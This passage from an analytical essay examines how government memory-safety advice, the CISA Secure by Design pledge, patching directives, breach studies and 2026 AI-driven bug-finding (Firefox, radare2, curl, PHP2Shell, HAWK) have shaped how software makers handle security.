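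The 2023 guide relied mainly on vulnerability counts. According to the figures it cited, memory-safety errors caused 70% of vulnerabilities at Microsoft and in Google's Chromium, 32 of Mozilla's 34 most serious flaws and, by Google's count, 67% of the zero-days of 2021. The White House gave more space to famous attacks, including the Morris worm, Slammer, Heartbleed, the 2016 spyware aimed at Ahmed Mansoor's iPhone, and another iPhone spyware exploit from 2023. The 2025 guide cited Heartbleed and BadAlloc, a set of flaws in the software of cars and industrial equipment.

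These attacks were old by the time the agencies wrote about them. Slammer, for example, was 21 years old, and no memory-safety disaster in 2022 or 2023 can explain why the advice came when it did. The agencies used attacks to illustrate their argument, but based it on two newer developments, published figures from large companies and the availability of Rust.

### The deadline of 1 January 2026

*Product Security Bad Practices* (2024), from CISA and the FBI, called several habits dangerous in software used for critical infrastructure, including default passwords, SQL injection, and starting new product lines in C or C++ where a memory-safe alternative was readily available. For existing products in such languages, it set a deadline for a roadmap that promised to reduce memory-safety flaws significantly, starting with the most important code. The FBI's published version exempted products whose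 makers had announced that support would end before 2030. It also accepted hardware protections as an alternative to a new language, so a company could meet the request without rewriting its code.

Crouse (2024) noted in *Software Makers Encouraged to Stop Using C/C++ by 2026* that these were recommendations, not mandatory rules. But Livesay (2025) called the list "controversial" in *CISA updates bad practices guide for product security based on stakeholder input* and reported that stakeholders saw it as a possible first step towards legal liability for insecure software. A court could treat an official list of bad practices as evidence of negligence. After receiving 78 public comments, CISA issued a second version in January 2025, three days before the change of administration, and kept the deadline.

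Neither agency appears to have counted the roadmaps that companies published. wrocpp's *C++ Safety State of the Union* (2026), an essay from a group of C++ programmers in Poland, describes companies without a roadmap as out of compliance with the policy, but concedes that the means of enforcing it are still undeveloped. The essay also wrongly calls the list a directive. No company is known to have been penalized for missing the date, which passed without a wave of announcements.

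The fullest statement of this kind from a large company is a paper Google published in March 2024 on its approach to memory safety, seven months before CISA and the FBI set the deadline. The paper described writing new code in memory-safe languages and adding checks to the remaining C++, but it gave no date for finishing. Without one, outsiders can judge the company's direction but not whether it is late.

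### The Secure by Design pledge

CISA started its Secure by Design campaign in April 2023 to move the burden of security from users to software makers. Its best-known part was a pledge for companies that sell software to businesses. By signing, a company promised to make a good-faith effort over the next year towards seven goals:

- More use of multi-factor authentication, a login that needs something besides a password
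- Fewer default passwords
- Fewer flaws of one or more whole classes, such as SQL injection or memory-safety flaws
- More customers installing security patches
- A public policy that lets outsiders test products and report flaws
- Complete and timely public records of vulnerabilities
- Logs that let customers see whether somebody has broken in

CISA's *Secure by Design Pledge* stated that it was voluntary and that the agency would not enforce it or check compliance. Each company could choose which class of flaw to reduce and how to show progress. These terms were negotiated, and Cybersecurity Dive reported that industry executives had pushed back against CISA's original plan, which had firmer commitments.

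On 8 May 2024, 68 companies signed CISA's Secure by Design pledge. The number of signers rose to 248 after six months and 267 by September 2025. Resilient Cyber's *A Digital Scouts Honor* noted that many signers were security companies, which stand to sell more if everyone else takes the goals seriously. Others, such as Fortinet, Ivanti and Citrix, make products that attackers have repeatedly exploited. Progress, whose MOVEit program Cl0p had attacked a year before the pledge, was not listed in CISA's *Secure by Design Pledge Signers*.

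Cable told The Record at the six-month mark that about 15 companies had published concrete progress reports, which had exceeded expectations. CISA planned to have an independent civil-society group assess the companies and to make the second year's pledge stricter. It did not intend to remove companies that failed, because it wanted customers to see who had kept the pledge. Neither the assessment nor the stricter pledge seems to have followed.

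The pledge's one-year period had ended for the first 68 signers by June 2025. CISA's *Secure by Design Progress Reports* then listed ten companies, which made up at most 15% of that group. The page was probably incomplete, since Cable had already counted more reports, but companies that wanted credit had good reason to send CISA a link. Of the 15 articles listed by title, eight were about logins, one was about reducing classes of vulnerability, and none mentioned memory safety.

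Some of the reported progress had other causes. Snowflake, a data-storage company, announced that by November 2025 it would block logins that used only a password. In 2024 criminals used stolen passwords to get into the accounts of many Snowflake customers, including AT&T and Ticketmaster, which is enough to explain the change. Microsoft began a security overhaul in November 2023, six months before the pledge, after Chinese hackers read US officials' email. The pledge gave these companies a place to report what attacks had already pushed them to do. It may also have sped up the work, as Cable said, but nobody has compared signers with similar companies that did not sign.

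### Retreat in Washington

After Donald Trump won the 2024 election, software companies saw a chance to reduce federal oversight. In March 2025 BSA, which represents major software makers, urged the White House to stop what it called "quasi-regulatory actions" on cybersecurity. It did not mention the Secure by Design campaign. Cable had left CISA when the Biden administration ended. In April the campaign's two remaining leaders, Bob Lord and Lauren Zabierek, accepted the new administration's offer of paid resignation. One person familiar with the campaign told Cybersecurity Dive that companies would "clap back" if CISA promoted the pledge again.

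The advice continued for a while after Lord and Zabierek announced their departure. Two months later, CISA and the NSA issued their guide to memory-safe languages, and CISA's *New Guidance Released for Reducing Memory-Related Vulnerabilities* still called such languages the most comprehensive protection against these flaws. But the government had begun to give up its strongest means of influence, its own buying power.

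In 2020 Russian spies got into several federal agencies through a tampered update from the software company SolarWinds. An executive order in 2021 led to a rule that agencies could use software only if its maker attested to following secure development practices, such as protecting the systems that build the product and checking code for known flaws. A senior executive or a delegate had to sign the attestation form, and a knowingly false answer could lead to prosecution. President Biden's last cybersecurity order, in January 2025, would also have required companies to submit evidence. President Trump cancelled that part in June 2025, and in January 2026 the White House budget office withdrew the attestation rule and left each agency to decide what to ask of software makers.

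The rule covered the development process, much like Microsoft's Security Development Lifecycle, so a company that wrote everything in C could truthfully sign the form. Still, it was the only US measure of the period under which software makers could lose federal sales, and it lasted less than two years after the form came out.

Lord and Zabierek launched a non-profit, the Software Safety Institute, on 9 November 2026. In *Introducing the Software Safety Institute*, Zabierek and Lord (2026) argue that the flaws AI is now finding belong to the same classes that topped the lists 20 years ago, and that telling users to patch faster "can't keep pace". The institute plans to measure the state of software security and press for policy changes. It asked for donations at its launch.

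### The 2026 directive on patching

The government did make faster patching compulsory for federal civilian agencies. On 10 June 2026, CISA issued Binding Operational Directive 26-04, which ordered them to fix flaws according to risk. CISA (2026) warned that AI may shorten the time between the release of a patch and the first attack.

A flaw's urgency depends on whether the affected system is open to the internet, whether attackers are already using the flaw, whether they can automate the attack, and how much control it gives them. Agencies must fix the worst flaws within three days and may put off the least dangerous, according to *CISA Orders Federal Civilian Agencies to Prioritize Vulnerability Patching by Risk* (Smith, 2026). The 180 days they were given to prepare end on 7 December.

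The directive binds software users, but it reaches some makers indirectly because FedRAMP (2026), the programme that approves cloud services for government use, made matching rules compulsory for providers from the same date. Other makers are only encouraged to follow it. SecurityWeek reported that CISA's previous directive on the subject did not penalise agencies that missed their deadlines, so even a binding order may have limited force.

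This was the clearest case in Washington of attacks leading to a rule, since CISA explicitly gave faster attacks as its reason. But the rule requires only the repair of flaws, and CISA knows the limits of that approach. *CISA review makes the case for eliminating vulnerability classes* (Zorz, 2026) summarises the agency's August 2026 review of the flaws that attackers used in 2024 and 2025. CISA found that 41.5% of the entries in its catalogue of exploited flaws belong to types that have been among the 25 most dangerous nearly every year since 2019. It also found that most break-ins came from ordinary criminals who searched the internet for known flaws.

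The review also used a 2007 standard from MITRE, which called some flaws "unforgivable" because the mistake was well documented and the attack trivial. Three of today's ten most common types of weakness would have qualified. CISA blamed company culture and urged software makers to remove whole classes of flaw. Three weeks later, it stopped publishing its weekly lists of new vulnerabilities to help companies focus on the dangerous ones among many AI-generated reports (Geller, 2026, *CISA ends weekly vulnerability roundups as part of shift to prioritization approach*).

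### Did the advice change engineering?

Government advice on memory safety came after companies had already begun adopting memory-safe languages. Microsoft recommended Rust in 2019, and Google announced Rust support in Android in April 2021, 19 months before the NSA's first document on the subject. The agencies then relied on those companies' figures, and their 2025 guide used Android as its case study. No large company is known to have started using a memory-safe language because an agency recommended it.

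The advice still had small effects. In 2024, engineers whose managers doubted the investment in Rust could cite several governments as well as Google in its favor. Google mentioned the agencies' support when it explained its use of Rust for the AirDrop link. *TRACTOR Benchmark for Evaluating C to Rust Translators* (2026) cites the White House report and the 2025 guide in its case for translating old C code automatically.

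The strongest sign of influence comes from the committee that sets the standard for C++. In February 2025 Bjarne Stroustrup, the creator of C++, warned its members of "unprecedented, serious attacks on C++" and of a painful decline unless they acted. The committee was under pressure from government advice and from programmers who preferred Rust. Its safety group's two main proposals were Safe C++, which would have added Rust-like rules to the language, and profiles, which would let programmers switch on sets of restrictions in ordinary C++. In a poll, 19 members preferred profiles, nine preferred Safe C++ and 11 wanted to pursue both.

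The C++ committee did not finish profiles in time for the 2026 standard and postponed them to 2029. It did include a hardened version of the standard library that stops a program when it reads past the end of a list. Google had already used such checks across hundreds of millions of lines of code, where they reduced speed by about 0.3% and exposed more than 1,000 bugs, according to wrocpp. Government advice to stop using C++ therefore helped to produce better hardening for people who still use it.

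One reason there are no stricter rules is that buyers and lawmakers have no agreed test of memory safety to refer to. Rust code with unsafe sections, C++ with extra checks, and old C on a processor with memory tags all offer some protection, and a buyer who asks for "memory-safe software" in a contract has not specified which of these is enough. *It Is Time to Standardize Principles and Practices for Software Memory Safety*, a paper with 21 authors, calls standards an essential next step, partly for this reason.

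Advice and law can be compared on the problem of default passwords, but only roughly, because nobody has counted the devices. Four years into Britain's voluntary code, most device makers still had no contact for reporting flaws. The Raspberry Pi dropped its default password before a law had passed, and its makers cited legislation as a reason. A similar comparison for software in general will not begin until 11 December 2027, when the main duties of the Cyber Resilience Act take effect.

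## What companies do after a breach: statistical studies

Famous cases such as Microsoft and Android may not be typical, but researchers have also followed hundreds or thousands of organisations and compared those that were breached with those that were not. Most of these organisations, such as hospitals and shops, use software rather than sell it.

### What attacked firms buy

*The Impact of Ransomware Attacks on Security Portfolios* (Hajizada, Itzhaki and colleagues, 2026) pairs each of 102 US organisations that disclosed a ransomware attack in 2019 or 2020 with one in the same industry, with a similar number of employees, that had not reported an attack. It compares the security products that both had installed in 2018 and 2022. Its method, difference-in-differences, estimates the effect of an attack by subtracting the change in the comparison group from the change in the attacked group.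 This assumes that the two groups would otherwise have changed by the same amount.

| Average per firm | Rise at attacked firms | Rise at other firms | Difference |
|---|---|---|---|
| Security functions covered, out of 5 | 0.88 | 0.41 | 0.47 |
| Core kinds of security product, out of 4 | 0.60 | −0.04 | 0.64 |
| All kinds of security product, out of 12 | 2.44 | 1.58 | 0.86 |
| Total number of security products | 4.13 | 2.62 | 1.51 (not statistically significant) |

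The five functions (identify, protect, detect, respond and recover) come from a framework published by NIST, the US standards agency. The four core product types are firewalls, login management, protection for individual computers, and systems that collect and analyse security records. Attacked firms added these products, while the other firms, on average, did not.

Attacked firms also bought more from vendors that sell several kinds of security product, but some of this was catching up. Before the attacks, they averaged 0.76 products from such vendors, compared with 1.04 at the other firms. By 2022, both groups averaged about 7.3.

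The sample is small, and the pairs match only on industry and size, so attacked firms may have differed from their matches in other ways that also affected their later purchases. The database also changed its product categories between 2018 and 2022, which affected both groups but makes the totals hard to interpret. All of these products are for hardening or recovery and are added around the software a firm already has. The data do not show whether any firm replaced the program that let the attackers in.

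### Whom they hire

*Human Capital Acquisition in Response to Data Breaches* (Bana, Brynjolfsson and colleagues, 2022) uses online job advertisements from 2010 to 2020 to compare 1,435 firms that had a breach with 87,628 that did not, in the six months before and after each announcement. The table shows the rise in the chance that a breached firm advertised each type of job in a given month.

| Type of job | First three months | Next three months | Six-month average |
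|---|---|---|---|
| Cybersecurity | 1.3 points | 3.4 points | 2.1 points |
| Legal or public relations | 1.5 points | 4.0 points | 2.1 points |

In a typical month, about 21 more of every 1,000 breached firms advertised a security job than would have without the breach. The increase in firms advertising for lawyers and publicists, who deal with the consequences of a breach rather than its cause, was nearly as large. The number of security advertisements rose by 0.4 a month, while the rise in legal and publicity advertisements was not statistically significant.

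Two checks support the claim that breaches caused the hiring. Advertisements for unrelated jobs did not increase. Breaches involving lost devices or paper files had no effect on security hiring, while hacking and card fraud raised the chance of a company advertising a security job by 3.6 percentage points.

The new jobs were mostly for analysts and for database and network administrators, while hiring of network architects did not rise significantly. Bana and colleagues conclude that firms were mainly trying to detect attacks rather than prevent them. Firms whose breaches drew heavy news coverage and many online searches shifted their hiring towards security and away from publicity. This fits Microsoft's experience after Gartner told customers to abandon Microsoft's web server.

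Job advertisements don't show whether firms hired anyone, though, and the data miss firms that brought in contractors or retrained their own staff. Bana and colleagues also report no response among manufacturers and other producers of goods, but these made up only about 4% of the breached firms, or fewer than 60, which is too few to be sure of the result.

These responses may be small partly because breaches cost firms little. Bana and colleagues cite a review of earlier research in which listed companies, apart from a few catastrophic cases, temporarily lost about 0.3% of their share value. They also cite a survey in which only 11% of people stopped dealing with a firm after a breach. Hajizada and colleagues cite research in which firms raised security spending more when a breach was expensive or when an outsider discovered it, as the adoption rule would predict.

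A breach may even make rebuilding less likely. Hajizada and colleagues cite a 2025 study by Wang and colleagues, who found that breached firms spent more on IT overall but started fewer new IT projects. *Data breaches and corporate liquidity management* reports that breached US firms hold more cash and cut investment. Replacing an old system is a new project and a large investment, so these firms probably postpone it.

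### Whether the spending works

Juhee Kwon and Eric Johnson examined the security investments and breaches of 2,386 US hospitals over five years, and estimated how different investments affected a hospital's risk of a first breach. Johnson writes in *How Far Does Prevention Go When Securing Health Care Data?* that hospitals that invested before any breach had fewer security failures, and got more protection for their money, than those that invested in reaction to one.

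Security spending that follows an attack seems to be less effective than earlier spending, which is a warning against relying on attacks to improve security. But hospitals were not randomly assigned to invest early or late. Well-run hospitals probably invest earlier and also have fewer breaches for other reasons, such as better-trained staff, and the comparison cannot fully separate the effect of early investment from those other causes.

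The amount of security technology also seems to matter less than how an organisation uses it. Angst, Block and colleagues (2017) studied US hospitals too, and Security Magazine's *Greater Hospital IT Security Doesn't Mean Fewer Cyberattacks* (2018) reports that hospitals with more security systems did not have fewer breaches. Angst and colleagues distinguish substantive adoption, in which a hospital changes how it works, from symbolic adoption, in which it mainly wants to look secure. Bana and colleagues compare the two to installing a burglar alarm and putting an alarm company's sticker on the door.

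### Disclosure laws and old web servers

Attacks can also put pressure on firms that haven't been attacked, if a law makes breaches more embarrassing. In September 2002, California passed the first US law requiring companies to tell customers about breaches. Hackers had broken into a state data centre that held information about legislators and state employees, and its managers had kept quiet about it for two months. The legislature then passed the bill with no votes against.

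Murciano-Goroff (2019), in *Do Data Breach Disclosure Laws Increase Firms’ Investment*, tested whether California's breach disclosure law led firms to keep their web servers up to date. Servers usually report which version of their software they run, and the Internet Archive had saved this information for 213,810 US companies. The estimate of the law's effect uses only about 15,000 firms that ran the Apache web server between 2000 and 2005. All were in local trades such as restaurants, shops and nursing homes, so those outside California would have had few Californian customers and little reason to react to the law.

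The law made Californian firms' server software about 0.33 months (roughly ten days) newer than it would otherwise have been. The average server ran software 19 months old. The effect was larger at firms with more than 250 employees, at about a month and a half.

These gains would have prevented very few attacks. In a later sample of 172,613 firms, 423 of which had a recorded hack, firms with older server software were more likely to have been hacked. Murciano-Goroff reports that the odds of a hack rise 18.5% with each extra month of age, but the calculation uses the logarithm of age, so the 18.5% increase actually corresponds to software 2.7 times as old. The odds are about 12% higher for software twice as old. If the relationship is causal, making software 1.7% newer lowers the odds by only about 0.3%.

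A warning about a specific flaw had a more visible effect than the law. In July 2002, the announcement of a security bug in Apache led so many firms to update that the average age of servers dropped sharply, both inside and outside California. Murciano-Goroff left out the months before this drop to avoid mistaking it for an effect of the law. The drop, like the response to Heartbleed, shows that firms can repair quickly when the danger is specific and the fix is ready.

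The study's main weakness is that only one state had the law, so anything else that happened to Californian firms in those years, such as the after-effects of the dot-com crash, could look like an effect of disclosure. Local shops also tend to hold less valuable data than the companies the law was most likely to embarrass. The law had no measurable effect on firms using Microsoft's server, but that server reveals only its major version, so the data would not show whether they had installed patches.

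By 2018 every state had a disclosure law, but researchers disagree about whether the laws reduced breaches. *Privacy Breaches and the Effect of Customer Notification* reports significantly fewer breaches after the laws, and says that affected firms were more likely to appoint executives with IT expertise. Bana and colleagues cite a 2021 study by Greenwood and Vaaler that found no fall in the number or size of breaches. The effect is hard to measure because disclosure laws also make more breaches known.

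The laws depend on customers leaving firms that have had a breach. In *Sound and Fury, Signifying Nothing?*, Hydari, Liang and Telang (2024) describe this as the main way the laws should work, but question whether it works after analysing a large breach.

### Rewarding programmers for secure code

*Security Incentivization* (Rass, Pinzger and colleagues, 2026) reports an experiment in rewarding secure code directly, with 84 undergraduates at the University of Klagenfurt in Austria. The reward was bonus marks, enough to raise a student's final result by a full grade, although the paper's subtitle mentions micropayments.

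The students worked in 14 teams, each of which wrote an Android game and its server program. Eight teams could earn the bonus by reducing the number of warnings per line of code that three automatic security scanners produced. The other six could earn the same bonus for general code quality. Both groups saw both sets of results, so the only intended difference was which set counted toward the bonus.

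The teams rewarded for security had a median of 5 warnings per 100 lines of code, compared with 8 for the others. This difference was statistically significant until the researchers accounted for project stage and whether the code belonged to the game or the server. The bonus was based on the change in warnings between stages, which did not differ significantly between the groups either.

By the end of the first stage, before anyone could earn a bonus, the security teams' server code already had about two-thirds fewer warnings. Those students knew that a bonus was coming, and that may have influenced them. But the researchers assigned the reward by course section, and three of the four instructors taught only one of the two groups, so differences in teaching or ability could also explain the gap. The experiment is weak evidence that rewards change how people write code.

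The students can represent programmers but not companies, because the experiment rewarded security and the main doubt about companies is whether their managers will pay for it. The students also had no customers waiting for new features, and they had no formal security training, so they had more easy mistakes to fix than professionals would.

Rass and colleagues acknowledge that a scanner warning is often not a real vulnerability. All the code was in Kotlin or Java, which are memory-safe, so the rewards could lead students to fix individual problems but not to adopt a safer language.

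### What persuades managers to pay

For *Identifying How Firms Manage Cybersecurity Investment* (2015), Moore, Dynes and Chang interviewed 40 executives, most of them heads of information security. Of these, 88% said their budgets had grown. Most interviewees attributed senior managers' support to breaches in the news, particularly the one at the health insurer Anthem. Five said they lacked adequate support, and their firms had not had recent security problems. This is the best direct evidence that attacks, including those on other companies, lead firms to increase their security budgets.

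The executives mostly followed industry practice and frameworks (checklists of recommended protections) when deciding how to spend the money. They most often chose reducing risk and complying with rules as their reasons for investing, and few chose customers' requirements. ENR's *Survey Tells How Firms Manage Investing in Cybersecurity* notes that the firms focused more on process than on results. When managers did object to a plan, they often doubted that the security team could hire enough people to carry it out.

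IBM sponsored the research and recruited most of the participants, who were reporting their own success at getting funding. The study had no comparison group, and Moore and colleagues say the findings do not generalise to the whole profession.

Memory safety appears to be harder to sell than checklists, though the evidence is weaker than it looks. Rahman and colleagues write that it is difficult to sell to senior leadership, but they do so in their introduction to the topic in a report on the September 2024 industry summit. *S3C2 Summit 2024-08* (Miller, Enck and colleagues, 2025) contains the same sentence and covers a similar meeting of 14 people from 10 US government agencies. Neither report attributes the remark to anyone who attended.

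The government participants explained what was holding them back. Translating old code by hand was often too expensive, and they had no reliable tools to do it automatically. Rust was hard to learn, which made it harder to recruit and train programmers, and some participants worried about its speed. Those in the space industry added that Rust programs tended to report more errors under high radiation than their existing C and C++ code.

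The company engineers wanted better tools for combining Rust with C++ so that they could switch languages gradually. These are all complaints about cost. Neither report's discussion of memory-safe languages mentions a breach that persuaded managers to pay for the switch.

Some government participants had won colleagues over by dropping security jargon and explaining the consequences of poor security in terms each person cared about. Others wanted the law to make software companies liable for security failures, as in Europe. Both meetings were small, private and attended by people already interested in the subject, so the participants' managers may be more sympathetic than most.

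### What the studies rarely measure

Researchers have counted security products, job advertisements, server versions and breaches because outsiders can get data on these, but can rarely see how a company builds its software. None of these studies of firms measured the share of new code in memory-safe languages, the use of database libraries that reject unsafe queries, or the number of formally verified components. The student experiment examined code, but the students had chosen their languages for other reasons.

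The studies could also have missed slow changes. Microsoft approved its Security Development Lifecycle three years after Code Red, and Android announced support for Rust in the operating system almost six years after Stagefright. A study covering only the six months after a breach would not have included either change.

Researchers could fill part of this gap by studying open-source projects, whose code and full history are public. They could pair projects that had a serious, widely exploited flaw with similar projects that did not, and compare which programming languages each group used for new code over the following five years.

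## AI bug-finding in 2026 and how software makers responded

On 7 April 2026 the AI company Anthropic announced that its newest model, Claude Mythos Preview, had found thousands of serious flaws in widely used software. Criminals could have used the model to find flaws to attack, so Anthropic did not release it to the public. Instead, through Project Glasswing, it gave access to a group that soon numbered about 50 organisations, including Microsoft and Cisco, so that they could fix flaws in their software before attackers had a model as good.

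After one month, the partners had found more than 10,000 flaws of high or critical severity, according to Anthropic's *Project Glasswing* (2026). Cloudflare, which carries traffic for many websites, found 2,000 bugs, 400 of them serious. Several partners told Anthropic that they were finding flaws more than ten times as fast as before.

### How cheap finding flaws became

Mozilla tried two models on its Firefox browser within a few months, which gives a good measure of the change. *Partnering with Mozilla to improve Firefox's security* (Ben Asher, Lucas and colleagues, 2026) reports that Claude Opus 4.6 found 22 vulnerabilities in two weeks. Mozilla rated 14 of them high-severity, almost a fifth of the number of high-severity vulnerabilities it fixed in all of 2025. Mythos Preview then found 271 vulnerabilities.

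Cheap bug-finding did not require the restricted model, Mythos. At the Black Hat security conference in August, Yan Shoshitaishvili of Arizona State University described searching the Linux kernel with undergraduate students and older GPT models. According to WeLiveSecurity's *Black Hat USA 2026* (2026), they first found about 300 flaws, compared with 479 that the press had credited to Mythos. They found about 600 with a better workflow, and about 1,000 after training the models on known flaws. By then, the students were finding flaws faster than they could write reports.

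Anthropic opened its next model, Mythos 5, to more defenders in August. In November it released Mythos 5.2, which is even better at finding vulnerabilities, according to *Anthropic Rolls Out Mythos 5.2 With Improved Bug Hunting, Fewer Sandbox Escapes* (Kovacs, 2026).

### Flaws that defenders found

Anthropic publishes running totals for the open-source projects it scans. The May figures come from its first update and from Coopersmith (2026), in *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard*, and the November figures come from Anthropic (2026).

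| | 22 May 2026 | 2 November 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Possible flaws found | 23,019 | 37,966 |
| Flaws reported to maintainers | 1,596 | 5,087 |
| Projects that received reports | 281 | 680 |
| Reported flaws known to be patched | 97 (6%) | 629 (12%) |
| Reported flaws not known to be patched | 1,499 | 4,458 |

Between the two dates, Anthropic reported 3,491 more flaws and learned of 532 more patches, or about one patch for every 6.6 reports. The gap is partly because maintainers had only days to deal with the latest reports. Anthropic also sent 3,225 of the reports to maintainers without an outside check, so some may be wrong. Even so, the number of unpatched flaws tripled in five months.

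VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026) is more critical and says that makers had fixed only 217 flaws. KIberblick's *Glasswing* (2026), a German comparison of the two sets of figures, explains that VulnCheck counted the flaws marked "fixed" in Anthropic's ledger, while Anthropic's 629 includes every fix that a maintainer has released. Anthropic's figure is the better measure of repair. KIberblick also notes that VulnCheck sells vulnerability data and that VulnCheck's post ends with an advertisement.

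Anthropic's figure of 94.2% for the share of real flaws covers only the 6,376 candidates that outside security firms reviewed, or 17% of the total. It also counts flaws that maintainers already knew about or do not intend to fix. Claude tends to rate flaws as more serious than maintainers do. In one analysis that KIberblick cites, Claude rated 91.5% of flaws high or critical, while maintainers gave those ratings to 51.3%.

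Companies patched their own code much faster than open-source projects did. In the first three weeks of Claude Security, a scanning product for businesses, customers used it to patch over 2,100 vulnerabilities. A serious flaw in an open-source project took two weeks to patch on average, and some maintainers asked Anthropic to slow down. Anthropic says this is because a company can fix its own code at once, while an open-source fix usually has to wait for a volunteer.

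### Flaws that attackers used

VulnCheck has traced 442 published vulnerabilities to Anthropic, about 0.5% of the 93,450 that all sources published in 2026 up to early November. Attackers had used two of the 442 by then. Attackers are estimated to eventually use at most 6% of published vulnerabilities, which would be at most about 26 of these. One of the two was a SQL injection flaw in Ghost, a program for running blogs and newsletters. Hackers had first described that kind of attack 27 years earlier.

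VulnCheck treats the low number as a sign that Anthropic exaggerated the danger. The number would also be low if Anthropic's precautions had worked, since it told the software makers first and kept the details of most flaws private. The count cannot show which explanation is right. It also omits any flaws that attackers found with their own AI models, which nobody can count until a victim or researcher notices an attack.

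Mandiant estimated that attacks in 2025 already began, on average, before the flaw was disclosed. No full-year average for 2026 is available yet. A patch shows which code its maker changed, and therefore where the flaw was. *Патч Firefox теперь подсказывает хакерам, как ломать старые версии* (Antipov, 2026) reports that Mozilla has seen signs that a Chinese model, GLM 5.3, can use Firefox patches to work out attacks on older versions. If so, people who delay an update are in more danger after the patch than before it.

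### Firefox: 423 fixes in a month

Mozilla began with a batch of reports from Anthropic in February, then built its own system. Each copy of the model looks for flaws in one file and has to write a test that triggers any flaw it suspects. If the test doesn't trigger the flaw, the claim never reaches an engineer. This removed most of the false reports that had made earlier AI tools useless to Mozilla.

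Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* (2026) reports that Mythos Preview found 271 of the flaws fixed in Firefox 150, of which 180 were high severity, 80 moderate and 11 low. Mozilla fixed 423 security bugs in total in April, compared with 20 to 30 in a typical month of 2025. Over 100 people contributed code, and the post mentions long workdays.

Some of the flaws were 15 or 20 years old, which weakens Google's case for leaving old code alone. For years, automated testing had missed an integer overflow, similar to the Stagefright flaws in Android, in the code that lays out tables.

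Mozilla's earlier work on prevention was still effective in 2026. Researchers had several times escaped Firefox's sandbox by tampering with shared JavaScript objects in the browser's privileged part. Mozilla had responded by freezing those objects by default, so that nobody could change them, rather than fixing each case. Its logs from 2026 show that the model tried this route many times and failed. Without the earlier change, these attempts would have added to the 271 repairs.

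The 2026 fixes repaired existing flaws. Mozilla planned to have the models check each code change as programmers submit it. This would catch flaws earlier, but programmers could still make the same mistakes.

### radare2 and curl: the maintainer's side

radare2 is a free toolkit for taking apart compiled programs. It has over a million lines of code, and one person, who writes as pancake, maintains most of it as a hobby. In October the project signed up for a free scanning service from Anthropic. pancake (2026), in *Myths in R2Land*, describes receiving 372 reports in a single email at one in the morning, two weeks later. Each came with a way to reproduce the flaw, and pancake spotted no false ones. The project's own rules called for publishing and fixing every known vulnerability within 24 hours.

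pancake's employer, the security company NowSecure, agreed to a couple of weeks of paid time for the work. With the help of AI models, pancake fixed about 200 of the flaws in four days. The patches that Anthropic suggested often treated the symptom, missed the reasons behind the design, or left similar bugs in nearby code. Following up one report could turn up four more flaws, and the list grew to about 1,500 entries, including duplicates. Some of them need a broader redesign. That is a small sign that a flood of reports can point a maintainer towards prevention, though so far pancake has described the need for redesign and carried out repairs.

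curl, a program that transfers data for a very large number of devices, had a worse experience. In May its lead developer, Daniel Stenberg, spent hours on five flaws that came with the label "confirmed" and ended up with one vulnerability of low severity, as KIberblick recounts. Of 34 later reports that curl made public, its developers had rejected 19 as not being vulnerabilities, accepted six as low-severity and not yet judged nine. curl is much smaller than radare2 and many researchers had already searched it, so the models probably had less to find. On 26 October curl stopped accepting private reports of low- and medium-severity flaws, citing an "avalanche". Reporters now have to post them publicly.

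### PHP: a warning, a deadline and a second round

Two PHP flaws, known together as PHP2Shell, let an outsider run code on a server without logging in. They led governments to take websites offline in October. An AI review had first alarmed PHP's developers about the flaws in August.

| Date (2026) | Event |
|---|---|
| 20–21 October | The flaws become public, PHP releases fixes, and CISA urges everyone to install them at once |
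| 25 October | Several researchers have worked out how to exploit the flaws |
| 26 October | CISA adds them to its catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities |
| 29 October | Deadline for US federal civilian agencies to patch |
| 19 November | News of seven more critical fixes |

As of 21 October, CISA had seen no attacks, according to *Patch PHP Vulnerabilities Now* (gHale, 2026). The later evidence is confused. *CISA, security researchers confirm successful exploitation of PHP flaws* (Jones, 2026) treats CISA's catalogue entry as confirmation of successful attacks. But *CISA warns of PHP bug exploitation attempts* (Greig, 2026) points out that CISA's definition of exploitation includes failed attempts, and that the agency would not say whether the attempts it had seen were successful. Two security firms, Sophos and Palo Alto Networks, announced successful attacks and then withdrew the claims.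 By 27 October the feared mass attacks had apparently not happened, according to *5 Latest Updates On PHP2Shell Exploitation* (Alspach, 2026).

Researchers took about five days to produce a working exploit for flaws that affected most of the web and had the whole industry's attention. That was quick, but it gave careful operators time to patch. Many operators did not patch in that time. Greig cites a count by the security firm Censys of 42 million PHP services, of which a little over 10 million, about a quarter, had the patch after six days. After Heartbleed, the largest websites patched within a day or so, but the Censys count includes small and abandoned sites, some of which run PHP versions so old that their owners probably cannot update them.

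The three-day deadline for agencies matches the limit that CISA's June patching directive sets for the worst flaws. CISA also told operators to take PHP systems offline if they could not patch them, and said that firewalls might help for a while. The whole response was repair, except for the firewalls, which are a temporary kind of hardening. One of the seven later fixes corrected the incomplete October patch (Arghire 2026, *PHP Patches Seven Critical RCE Vulnerabilities*).

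### HAWK: a design that nobody had used yet

A digital signature proves who wrote a message and that nobody has altered it. HAWK, a candidate for a US standard for signatures that quantum computers could not forge, had survived two years of expert review. On 28 July Anthropic published an attack in *Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude* that effectively halves the strength of HAWK's keys. The AI model Mythos Preview, working with one researcher, found the attack in 60 hours using about $100,000 of computing. PostQuantum.com reports that HAWK's designers withdrew the scheme the next day.

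Nobody had built HAWK into a product, so dropping it did not affect users. In the adoption rule, C was close to zero, and the designers' reputations gave them a reason to act quickly. If the same discovery had come after ten years of use, replacing HAWK would have been slow and expensive. The comparison with PHP suggests that AI searches are most useful before software has users.

| Software | What the makers received | Response | Depth |
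|---|---|---|---|
| Firefox | 271 flaws from one model | Over 100 people contributed fixes | Repair |
| radare2 | 372 reports in one email | One maintainer fixed about 200 in four days | Repair, with some redesign to consider |
| PHP | Two critical flaws, then seven more | Emergency patches and a federal deadline | Repair, with temporary hardening |
| HAWK | One attack on the design | Withdrawal the next day | Prevention |

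### Signs of deeper change since April

Most of the changes software makers have announced affect how fast they patch and how they handle bug reports. Firefox has released new versions more often since September. Palo Alto Networks put over five times as many patches as usual into one release, and Oracle reported a similar increase. curl changed its rules for reporting bugs. These changes will probably last, because the volume of reports will not soon return to its old level, but none of them changes how programmers write code.

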